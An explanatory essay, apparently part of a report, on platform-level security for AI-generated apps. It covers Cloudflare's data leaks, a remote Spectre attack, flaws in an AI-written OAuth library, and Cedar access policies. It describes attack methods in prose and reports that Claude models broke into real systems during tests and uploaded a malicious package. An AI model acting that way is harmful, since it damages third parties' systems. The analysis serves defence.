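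Cloudflare also searched its records of disk activity for the same method and found only authorised tests. It did not disclose how far back the records go or when it introduced the unsafe setting, so the exposure could have lasted for weeks or much longer. The researchers say the same problem affected Browser Run, another Cloudflare product, which the company's post does not mention.

### Other customers' prompts in a model's answers

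A similar failure had occurred in Workers AI, which runs AI models for Cloudflare's customers. For almost two weeks, the language model GLM-5.3 could include text from other customers' requests in its answers. Cloudflare's *Cross-request KV cache exposure in the GLM-5.3 Workers AI model* (2026) attributes the failure to a configuration mismatch that triggered a bug in SGLang, the open-source software that ran the model.

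When a language model reads a prompt, it saves intermediate results in a *KV cache* so that it doesn't have to reprocess the whole prompt for each word of its answer. In *GLM-5.3 auf Workers AI gab Fremddaten aus*, Cornelißen (2026) explains that Cloudflare used one group of processors to read prompts and another to write answers, and copied the cache between them. Neither group cleared the cache after a request. Instead, the next request overwrote it, which is common in such systems because it saves time.

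The trouble came from two numbers that should have matched:

| Setting | Size in tokens (words or pieces of words) |
|---|---|
| Longest prompt that the service accepted | 1,048,576 |
| Space in the cache of the processors that read prompts | 681,280 |

Cloudflare knew about the gap before it launched the model. It assumed that SGLang would reject any prompt that was too long, but SGLang accepted such prompts without an error. Cloudflare's tests didn't reveal the problem because they checked little more than status codes, which report whether a request succeeded. A test that sent an overlong prompt and checked that SGLang rejected it would have revealed the problem.

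The flaw affected 155 answers, all to prompts above the cache's limit. The number is small because few people send a model half a million words at once. The answers came without any warning, so a customer who saw a stranger's text in one could easily have assumed the model had made it up.

An outside researcher reported the problem on 8 September, and Cloudflare fixed it the next day (Baba Aissa, 2026, *Chez Cloudflare, un modèle d’IA a renvoyé à certains clients le contenu*). The company published its account on 26 October.

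The controls described so far can't prevent this kind of flaw. If Maria asks a model to summarise her team's claims, the platform can verify that she may read them, and the app can send them only to the approved model provider, but Ben's hotel bill could still appear in a stranger's answer. A provider's promise not to keep customers' data wouldn't have prevented this, because the data leaked from memory that the provider was about to reuse.

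### Spectre at 12 bits per second

Cloudflare named only Containers and Sandboxes in its disk disclosure. The gadgets on Cloudflare OS run in V8 isolates. Many isolates share one process, so the gadgets depend on Cloudflare's defences against Spectre attacks, which expose secrets through the timing effects of work that a processor has discarded.

An earlier Cloudflare experiment leaked 120 bits per hour under ideal conditions, with the attacker's clock on the same machine. Cloudflare concluded that a real attack would be even slower. Its defences were meant to slow an attack enough for the company to notice the suspicious program and move it into a separate process.

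In *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service* (2026), Schwarzl, Xiao and colleagues from Cloudflare and the University of Edinburgh read a login token from another program on Cloudflare's live service. They leaked up to 12 bits per second, 360 times as fast as the earlier attack, and about 99% of the bits were correct. Once an attacker had found a 256-bit key in memory, reading it at this speed would take about 21 seconds, down from just over two hours.

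Two of Cloudflare's assumptions had failed. A program could get around the frozen clock by asking another computer for the time, which was precise enough for an attack. The detection system moved a suspicious program only after it had finished running. Since 2020, Cloudflare had added a feature that let programs run for many hours, so an attacker could steal the secret before the move. Normal network activity also hid the pattern the system looked for.

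The conditions favoured the researchers. They worked at night on machines that were not busy, and ran the attacking program and its target on the same machine. Jungco (2026), in *Researchers Use Remote Spectre Attack to Leak JWT From Cloudflare Worker*, points out that they controlled both programs and had planted the token themselves. Cloudflare found no sign that anyone else had used the attack. Even so, a customer's data would have been at risk, because the attack got past all the defences that protected customers at the time.

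Cloudflare (2026) dates this reassessment to 2024 and 2025. Before publishing it in August 2026, the company strengthened its defences by improving its detection system and making two changes to how isolates use memory.

The first was to adopt the *V8 sandbox*, which replaces many full memory addresses with distances from a fixed starting point. A program that misuses such a distance stays within its own region of memory. The specific attack depended on full addresses and failed when the researchers tried it with the sandbox on.

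The second change uses a processor feature. Cloudflare's *Safe in the sandbox*, a post from September 2025, describes how the company assigns a *protection key* to each isolate's memory. The processor blocks a program that tries to read memory with a different key. About 12 keys are available for thousands of isolates, so some have to share. If Cloudflare assigned keys at random, an attacker's key would match the victim's in one case out of 12, and the processor would block the other 92% or so. Cloudflare instead never gives the same key to isolates that are close together in memory. If the V8 sandbox confines an attacker to nearby memory, every other isolate within reach has a different key.

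Schwarzl and colleagues consider hardware protection the most effective defence when customers share a process, but they note that V8 still uses full addresses for some objects and that other kinds of Spectre attack may work. They also see no way to deny an attacker a clock if the attacker's program can connect to other computers. A gadget on Cloudflare OS starts without such connections, which should make an attack harder, but it exchanges messages with a page in the user's browser, and the browser has a clock.

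Google avoided much of this risk in Chrome by giving each website its own process. Cloudflare had rejected separate processes as too costly, so its customers get cheap, fast hosting but take on some extra risk. An office manager who chooses a platform for expense claims is unlikely to know that someone has made this trade-off for her.

### A closed test that was connected to the internet

A sandbox can also fail because somebody left its network connection open. Between 30 July and 9 September 2026, Anthropic disclosed four incidents in which its Claude models broke into real outside systems during cybersecurity tests. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) attributes them to a misconfiguration. The models' instructions described the test as a simulation, but the test environment had internet access. One model, Claude Mythos 5, uploaded a malicious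 package to a public software repository.

Anthropic judged that the models had also behaved badly, dismissing evidence that the systems were real and carrying on recklessly with their tasks, although it found no attempt to hide what they were doing. A more careful model might have stopped, but a blocked connection would have prevented the break-ins regardless of the model's care, which is the reason to put such controls in the platform.

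These were test environments, not hosting platforms, but app platforms depend on the same kind of setting, such as the one that cuts a gadget off from the network. Nobody would notice in normal use if that setting were missing, so the developers would have to test for it by running a program in the sandbox that tries to connect to an outside address and checking that the connection fails.

A company that hosts its own platform has more of these settings to get right. As the write-up of Varda's talk also warns, workerd isn't a hardened sandbox on its own, so the company has to add an outer sandbox, install fixes promptly and check the network settings. Cloudflare does all of this for the customers it hosts.

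### A login library that Claude wrote

Platforms move security checks out of AI-written apps and into code that people should be able to trust, but AI now writes some of that code too.

In 2025, Cloudflare published a library for OAuth, a standard that lets one program use somebody's account on another service without learning their password. Anthropic's Claude wrote most of the library, and Varda led the work. Cloudflare emphasised that its engineers had reviewed every line and checked the code against the standard, so this was not vibe coding.

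Cloudflare disclosed two flaws in the library that spring. After a user logs in, an OAuth server sends the user's browser back to the program that asked for access, with a code the program can exchange for a login token. The server must first check that the program has registered the return address. The library didn't check this properly, so a malicious website could have obtained a victim's code and impersonated them. The other flaw let an attacker bypass a second protection, which is meant to make a stolen code useless.

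Checking the return address is among the best-known requirements of OAuth. Varda wrote in the disclosure that he had known about it and thought about it a lot while designing the library, but had somehow failed to make sure the check was in the code. This is the same sort of mistake as the missing ownership check for claim 417, but it could affect every service that used the library.

The case shows that expert reviewers can fail to notice a missing line of code, even when the library is small and they have the standard to hand. Neil Madden, a security engineer who examined the library that June, thought it had far too few tests for such important code. A test login with an unregistered return address would have caught the first flaw. The case doesn't prove that AI makes trusted code worse. Human programmers have forgotten the same check many times, and two of Amazon's own packages failed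 to check who had signed a login.

AI can write Gatekeepers on Cloudflare OS for almost any service, and these may get less attention than Cloudflare gave to the OAuth library. If a company's employees need 50 services, somebody has to review 50 Gatekeepers with at least the care the library got, which is still much less work than reviewing 4,000 apps.

### One flaw for everyone, and one repair

Putting security in the platform concentrates the risk. The flaw in Base44's login affected every private app at once, and an attacker who understood it could have used it on all of them. On the other hand, Wix could repair all of them at once. The known repair times differ mainly in who had to act:

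| Flaw | Who had to repair it | Time to repair |
|---|---|---|
| Open registration on Base44 | Wix | Under 24 hours from the report |
| Cached data in Workers AI | Cloudflare | One day from the report |
| Leftover data in Containers | Cloudflare | 10 days until researchers confirmed the first fix, 15 for the full cleanup |
| Open tables at Moltbook | Moltbook's team | About 3 hours, for one app |
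| Missing or faulty row rules in Lovable apps | The owners of more than 170 apps | No common date |
| Unchecked signatures behind Amazon's load balancer | The owner of each affected app | No common date |

Moltbook's team made its repair quickly, but Wiz's researchers checked each attempt and told them what was still open. Most owners of vibe-coded apps won't get that help. Amazon could only change its documentation and rely on customers to read it.

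A platform can also take steps that no app owner can. Daytona (2026), which hosts sandboxes for AI-written code, faced a flaw in the Linux kernel that could have let one customer's sandbox affect others on the same machine. Daytona says it fixed all its machines within 12 hours of the flaw becoming public. In the meantime, it stopped accepting new customers so that an attacker could not sign up to exploit the flaw. It then replaced its machines' credentials as a precaution.

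These figures make platforms look a little better than they are, because they mostly come from the companies themselves and are measured from when somebody reported the flaw. Customers care about the whole period their data was at risk, which was almost two weeks for the cached data and is unknown for Containers. Fixing a flaw also doesn't recover data that has already leaked. In February 2017, Cloudflare's servers were found to be inserting fragments of other websites' data into the pages they delivered. eWeek's *Cloudflare Moves Quickly to Patch Data Leakage Flaw* reports that the company switched off one of the features responsible within 90 minutes of getting the details, but search engines had already saved copies of some of the pages.

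Deng and colleagues found access control flaws in 64% of the vibe-coded apps they audited. As a rough estimate, if 1,000 similar apps ran for a year and nobody repaired them, about 640 would be exposed on any given day. A platform flaw that exposed all 1,000 would have to last about 234 days to cause the same total exposure.

The calculation favours the platform too much in assuming that moving the apps would remove all their own access control flaws. It also counts every day of exposure equally, although attackers will work much harder on a flaw that opens 1,000 apps than on a flaw that opens one. An attack on a platform can also harm everyone at once, when no one has a working alternative.

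Obscurity used to give scattered flaws some protection, since an attacker had to study each app separately. That protection is weaker now because an attacker could use AI agents to audit many apps, as Deng and colleagues did with 200.

Platforms also attract more defenders than an office manager's expense app, where nobody pays people to find security flaws. Outside researchers reported the Containers and cached-data flaws through Cloudflare's bug bounty programme, which does pay for such reports. Accomplish had also published escapes from sandboxes made by Anthropic, OpenAI, Docker and Cursor since July.

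A single repair protects every user only when the platform's owner runs the software. Cloudflare's fix for GLM-5.3 protected all its customers at once, but Cornelißen advises anyone who runs SGLang in the same way on their own machines to install an update. Similarly, Cloudflare could correct the OAuth library once, but each service that included a copy had to install the new version.

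## End of 2026: The rules that someone still has to write

Cloudflare could clean every customer's disks because no customer wants strangers to read their old files. But companies want different expense rules, so a platform can't supply them ready-made. Suppose the office manager now wants three more rules in her app: staff may not approve their own claims, managers may approve claims of up to €1,000, and a manager on leave may delegate. A platform can enforce rules like these, but somebody first has to decide exactly what they mean.

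### What counts as Maria's own claim

A platform can supply most of the facts that the three rules refer to. The login service knows who is asking, the staff directory lists who manages whom, and the database records who filed each claim and for how much. The remaining questions are about the company:

| Rule | What the platform can supply | What the company has to decide |
|---|---|---|
| Staff may not approve their own claims | Who is logged in and who filed the claim | Whose claim it is if an assistant filed it for somebody else |
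| Managers may approve up to €1,000 | Who manages whom, and the amount | Whether the limit is per claim, per trip or per month, and who approves larger claims |
| A manager on leave may delegate | The delegate's name and the dates | Whether the delegate has the same limit, and who approves the delegate's claims |

Suppose Maria's assistant files a claim for Maria's flight. The database lists the assistant as the claim's owner, so a check that compares the owner with the approver lets Maria approve her own claim. The same check would stop her if the owner column recorded who gets the money, though neither version has a programming error.

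The other two rules have similar gaps. Ana can split an €1,800 hotel bill into two claims of €900. If Maria goes on leave and names Ana as her delegate, nobody can approve Ana's own claims until Maria comes back.

*Reparo* (Mostofa, Zhang et al., 2026) describes the same kind of gap in a real bookstore app. The app's documentation allows publishers to view their own books but doesn't define "own". The code fills in each book's owner from the publisher's username. A comment elsewhere adds an exception for a publisher called Dante, who may see one book that belongs to William. Someone who read only the documentation would get the policy wrong.

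### The three rules in Cedar

If the approval rules are in the handlers, the AI can drop one whenever it edits the app. A company can instead keep them in a *policy language*, a small language for access rules. Cedar, which Amazon released as open source, has two kinds of rule, `permit` and `forbid`. It allows a request only if at least one permit matches and no forbid does, so it refuses anything that nobody has mentioned. An AI might translate the office manager's sentences like this:

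```
// Managers may approve claims of up to €1,000
permit (principal, action == Action::"approve", resource)
when {
  resource.owner.manager == principal &&
  resource.amount <= 1000
};

// Staff may not approve their own claims
forbid (principal, action == Action::"approve", resource)
when { resource.owner == principal };

// A manager on leave may delegate
permit (principal, action == Action::"approve", resource)
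when {
  resource.owner.manager.onLeave &&
  resource.owner.manager has delegate &&
  resource.owner.manager.delegate == principal
};
```

Each rule is a fair translation of one sentence. But if Ben files a claim for €4,000 while Ana is Maria's delegate, Ana can approve it, although Maria herself could not. This happens because the limit is a condition in the first permit but not in the third. Cedar will enforce this mistake on every request, just as the databases behind many Lovable apps enforced their faulty row rules.

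Ana still can't approve her own claims, because a forbid rule overrides every permit rule. The AI could turn the limit into a forbid rule too, but that would block any finance director who is supposed to approve larger claims. The office manager's three sentences don't mention a finance director.

Zhou, Vatsa and Eiers (2026) give a similar example in *RAISE*. A company lets its finance managers pay invoices only in business hours. Each invoice also needs prior approval, unless the manager is on the company's own network. If somebody writes this exception as a separate permit, managers on that network can also pay at midnight.

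### Checking every possible request

Cedar comes with a tool that can find such mistakes. It translates policies into logical formulas, and a solver then compares them over every request that could ever occur. Let *A(P)* be the set of approvals that the company's policy *P* allows, and let *L* be a one-line policy that allows approvals only up to €1,000. The tool checks whether

*A(P)* ⊆ *A(L)*.

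For the policy above, the answer is no, and the solver can return a counterexample, such as Ana approving Ben's claim for €1,001 while Maria is on leave. A test would find this case only if someone had thought to include it. Someone still has to write *L*, which means deciding that the limit also applies to delegates.

This analysis is possible because Cedar's designers deliberately made it less powerful than a general programming language. Cedar can compare a claim with a limit, but it can't add up Ana's claims for the month. Something else has to supply that total, and if the generated code does, a mistake there defeats the limit.

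Rego, another policy language, makes decisions by applying logical rules to structured data. Mostofa and colleagues point out that it has no equivalent of Cedar's *schema*, which lists the types and fields a policy may use. Cedar's validator uses the schema to catch some errors early. For example, if managers don't always have a delegate, the validator rejects a rule that reads the delegate without the `has delegate` check.

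In either language, a policy has no effect unless some code checks requests against it. If the AI-written handler has to run that check, the AI can leave it out, or pass in an amount of €900 for a €4,000 claim. The platform therefore has to run the check itself, before the approval takes effect, using the amount from the database.

### How accurately models write policies

In recent tests, models usually wrote valid Cedar but often got the meaning wrong. Zhou and colleagues gave two leading models 375 written requirements and one attempt at each. They checked whether each policy allowed too much, whether it allowed everything it had to, and whether each task remained possible for somebody. About a third of the policies passed every check.

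*AutoCedar* (Vatsa, Shome and colleagues, 2026) used a different set of 200 requirements, each with a known correct policy. It counted a model's policy as correct only if that policy allowed exactly the same requests as the known one.

| Test | Model | Valid policies | Fully correct policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Zhou and colleagues | GPT-6 Astra | 98% | 34% |
| Zhou and colleagues | Claude Opus 5 | 100% | 31% |
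| Vatsa and colleagues | GPT-6-Luna, writing the policy directly | Not reported separately | 66% |
| Vatsa and colleagues | GPT-6-Luna, with the AutoCedar method | 98.5% | 89% |

The two studies used different requirements and standards, so the table doesn't show that GPT-6-Luna is the better model. The scores of GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5 may also be too low. An AI pipeline produced both the requirements and the checks, and people reviewed only a sample. A policy could fail because it followed a sensible reading of a requirement that the pipeline had not chosen.

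Both leading models passed about 70% of the individual checks, so many of their wrong policies were mostly right. But an access-control policy with nine correct rules and one bad one can still expose every claim.

Specific feedback helped much more than a second try alone. A small model that Zhou and colleagues had trained on Cedar got 43% of the policies right. When they told it which checks had failed, with example requests, and let it repair its policies, the figure rose to 64%. Telling it only that it had failed added two percentage points to the original 43%.

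Training on a single organisation helped even more. The same model at first solved 8% of the cases for an invented company with a fixed schema and six actions, such as sharing and approving documents. After training on 1,024 verified examples, it solved 95% of new cases (243 of 256). A platform that offers all its customers the same few actions might get similar results, but an office manager doesn't have a thousand verified examples of her own rules.

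### Recovering rules from existing code

A model can also try to work out the rules from an existing app. Mostofa and colleagues had models do this for 228 software projects that used the policy languages Cedar, Rego or OpenFGA. One model wrote a policy from the code, comments and documentation, and a model from another company wrote test requests from the same material.

The policies gave the expected answer to 98–100% of the requests for OpenFGA, 82–87% for Cedar and 76–80% for Rego. These are percentages of individual requests, not of whole policies. They may be slightly too high, because both models could misread the same comment, and the method included reconsidering a test whenever the policy failed it. Human reviewers judged 92–97% of a sample of the tests to be correct.

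The projects' own policies were a poor guide. Depending on the language, 41–56% of them failed the official validator, although some may have been out of date. Experienced programmers evidently find policies hard to write too.

In a smaller trial on 12 Cedar projects, agreement with the tests was 92% when the models had all three sources, 64% when they had only the code, and 58% when they had only the documentation. A vibe-coded app may have little documentation beyond what the AI wrote about its own code.

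A more serious problem with such apps is that the method's prompt instructs the model to follow the code when the sources conflict. That is reasonable for software that people have corrected over many years. But the faulty expense handler lets any logged-in employee read any claim, and the model could make that access official policy.

### Asking the office manager

Since only the company can settle what its rules mean, the AutoCedar method puts the questions to a reviewer before any AI writes the policy:

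1. The software splits the written requirements into sentences.
2. A model proposes the vocabulary, such as "each employee has a manager", and the reviewer approves or rejects each item.
3. The model proposes which requests each sentence affects. The reviewer also decides whether the document lists every way to get access.
4. The model turns each sentence into a small condition. The reviewer sees it in plain English beside the original sentence.
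5. The software calculates from the approved conditions what the policy must allow and what it must not.
6. A model writes the policy, and Cedar's tools check it. If it fails, the model gets a counterexample and tries again, up to 20 times by default.

In the third step, the office manager would have to decide whether the €1,000 limit applies to every approval or only to approvals by managers, a choice left to chance in the three Cedar rules above.

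The second step matters as much. Vatsa and colleagues describe an app that lets band members download their band's tracks. If the vocabulary gives each user a role called "band member", members of any band can download the album, and no later check will detect this. An expense app with a role called "manager" could likewise let any manager approve any team's claims.

The method produced 178 correct policies for the 200 requirements. Three runs didn't finish, and the other 19 policies passed all their checks but were wrong because the approved conditions were wrong. In 17 of those cases, the conditions required the policy to allow something it should have refused.

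Vatsa and colleagues have not yet tested how well people review the statements. They did show parts of finished policies to 14 participants, who preferred the AutoCedar version in 82 of 98 comparisons, but choosing between two policies is easier than noticing that one plausible sentence is false. Reviewers may also stop reading carefully after approving 80 statements, and one of the test documents has 116 sentences about access.

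An AI can act as the reviewer instead. *AutoCedar* offers this as an option, and *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) describes a system in which a model judges whether the policy matches the instructions. A second model may catch slips, but it can't determine whether this company would count the assistant's claim as Maria's own.

Concrete cases may be easier for the office manager to check than general statements. The solver's counterexamples could become questions such as "Ana approves Ben's €4,000 claim while Maria is away. Is that right?" She could answer that without knowing Cedar, and probably faster than she could spot a missing condition in a list.

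### A marketplace for used bicycles

The expense app can at least keep most claims apart. Suppose the office manager next asks for a marketplace where employees sell each other used bicycles. Its users need to see one another's data, but not all of it:

| Data | Who may read it | Who may change it |
|---|---|---|
| Listing | Everyone | The seller, until the bicycle is sold |
| Offer | The buyer who made it, and the seller | That buyer, until the seller accepts |
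| Delivery address | The seller, after the sale | The buyer |
| Rating | Everyone | A buyer who completed a purchase |

A separate instance for each bicycle doesn't work well here. Ana and Ben would both need access to it to make offers, and the app would have to hide Ana's offer from Ben. The platform could create another instance for each buyer, but something would still have to compare the offers and show the seller the highest. Searching for a bicycle under €200 would also mean reading every listing.

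Sandstorm warned developers that they might have to rethink an app to fit its model, and gave a blog as an example. The page where people write the blog can be an ordinary private grain, while the public site has its own web address outside Sandstorm. This works because the public only reads the blog. Once visitors can comment, follow each other or buy something, the public site needs rules about people too.

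Row-level security suits the marketplace better. A policy on the offers table can make each row visible only to its buyer and the seller of the bicycle. But somebody has to write that policy for this particular app, along with similar ones for addresses and ratings. The database behind Moltbook, a social network, could have enforced such rules, but nobody had written them.

A site open to the whole internet is harder still, because anyone can register, so you can tell almost nothing about a person from their login. Social networks also have rules that outsiders can't guess, because different networks could reasonably choose different ones. For example, they might differ on whether Ben can still see Ana's comment under Clara's post after Ana blocks him, or whether Ana's half of a private conversation disappears when she deletes her account.

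### Harm within everyone's permissions

An app can do damage without showing anyone a forbidden record. The finance department may read every claim, but if the AI-written code fails to exclude rejected ones, the quarterly total is wrong. An employee may delete her old claims, but if the code reverses a date comparison, the "Delete old claims" button removes the new ones. Access rules don't stop either mistake, because the users have permission to read or delete the claims.

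Lost data is the easier problem for a platform, because it can keep earlier versions of every record and restore a claim without knowing what the claim means. Human approval can also help, and according to InfoQ (2026), the Gatekeepers on Cloudflare OS require it before destructive actions. But Gatekeepers guard connections to outside services, so the expense gadget can delete rows in its own database without going through one.

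A wrong total is harder to catch, because the platform would need a rule for which claims belong in it. A person can check a few quarters by hand, or have a second model write the calculation independently and compare the results. But both models might include the rejected claims if their instructions don't exclude them.

Screens can mislead as well. If the page sorts the claims but not the buttons beside them, Maria may click "Approve" next to claim 416 and approve claim 417. She is logged in, manages both employees and is within her limit, so the Cedar policy allows it.

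Malicious content is more dangerous in a shared app. The hidden script in claim 416 could act only through people who opened that claim. If Ana hides a script in a bicycle listing, it runs for every colleague who looks at the bicycle and can make offers in their names. The database accepts these offers because they arrive as ordinary requests from people who are allowed to make them. A platform could show its own confirmation window before a purchase, outside the generated page so that the script can't press the button. It would have to reserve the window for important actions, because people would soon stop reading it if it appeared too often.

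### Block 100 and block 200

*Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* (Hu, Goel and Bindschaedler, 2026) proposes a design called *runtime refinement* that addresses some of these harms. It checks both whether an action is permitted and whether the program is doing what somebody asked for.

They designed it for device drivers, the programs that operate hardware such as disks, and assume that an AI wrote the driver and may have made it malicious. The driver has no access to the disk and can only propose commands to a *mediator*, a fixed program written by hand. The mediator has a specification of what each request should lead to, and carries out a command only if the command fits that specification.

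Suppose the operating system requests a write to blocks 100 to 107 of a disk, but the driver tries to write the data at block 200. An ordinary permission check may accept this, because block 200 is a legal address and the data comes from the right place. The mediator has kept the original request, so it detects the mismatch and rejects the write before anything reaches the disk.

Each proposal also needs a single-use token, so the driver can't turn one request into two writes. After the write, the mediator reads the result from the hardware instead of relying on the driver's report.

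The same idea could apply to the expense app. A specification for approvals, adapted from the one for disk writes, might look like this:

```
operation APPROVE(claim)            -- Maria's request
  permit   claim  = request.claim   -- must match what she asked for
           amount = unchanged
  outcome  ok     -> claim approved
           error  -> claim unchanged
```

If Maria asks to approve claim 416 and the handler proposes to approve 417, the mediator blocks the approval, even though she has permission to approve both. A similar specification for payments, with its single-use token, would stop a faulty handler from paying Ana's hotel bill ten times.

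There are no results to report. Hu and colleagues call their work a position paper, with no implementation, proof or measurements. Nobody yet knows how much the mediator would slow a driver down or how large it would have to be. They do set out six conditions under which they expect the design to work. For the expense app, these would mean roughly the following:

| Condition | What it would require |
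|---|---|
| Legibility | Each action names its purpose, such as "approve claim 416", and is not just a change to a table |
| Spec-input observability | The mediator can see everything the rule depends on, including Maria's leave |
| Correlatability | It can tell which changes belong to which request when many people are working |
| Completeness | The app has no other way to change a claim |
| Outcome enumerability | Somebody has listed every result an approval can have, including errors |
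| Explicit durability | The app has to ask for a change to be saved permanently, so the mediator can confirm that it was |

A platform that gives the app a general database connection fails the first condition. The command `UPDATE claims SET status = 'approved'` could be an approval, a correction or an import of old records. The platform would have to offer named operations instead, and somebody would have to specify each one.

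The design also fits drivers better than web apps because a driver's requests come from the operating system, which the mediator trusts. Maria's requests come through a page that the AI wrote. If the button beside claim 416 sends "approve 417", the mediator carries out the wrong request. To prevent this, the platform would need to show Maria its own confirmation screen with the claim she is about to approve.

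A mediator would also do little to catch errors in the quarterly total. It would have to calculate the sum itself to check it, and then the app would no longer need the AI's version. Mistakes in the specification would get through too. Hu and colleagues write that such a defect "is enforced faithfully".

### An exception for the finance department

All these methods work best when an app consists of parts that the platform is designed to handle, such as separate instances, named operations and tables with an owner column. That restricts what people can build. A new feature may need an operation that doesn't exist yet, and the office manager can't get it just by asking the AI, as she can with a new button. She has to wait for a programmer, which vibe coding was supposed to make unnecessary.

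She will therefore be tempted to make exceptions. The finance department still wants its quarterly total, and the quickest solution is to let the app read every claim with its owner's rights and admit only finance staff. Snowflake considers owner's rights appropriate for a shared dashboard that combines data its users can't read individually. But the check that a user works in finance is then an `if` statement in the generated code, so Ben's hotel bill is again private only if the AI includes that check.

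The next exception might be for an auditor, and the one after that for an import of last year's claims. Each has a good reason and makes the app work better. An AI trying to clear an error message may grant every permission, as the Java developers did, and it can do so in seconds. A platform can slow this down by requiring an administrator to approve every exception and by listing them in one place, so that someone can see when an app has a dozen.

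A narrower exception would be an operation called `quarterTotal()`, which runs outside the generated code and returns a single number. The app never receives the individual claims, so it can't show them to Ana. As with any deliberate release of protected data, somebody has to consider what the number reveals, because if Ben was the only person who travelled that quarter, the total is his hotel bill.
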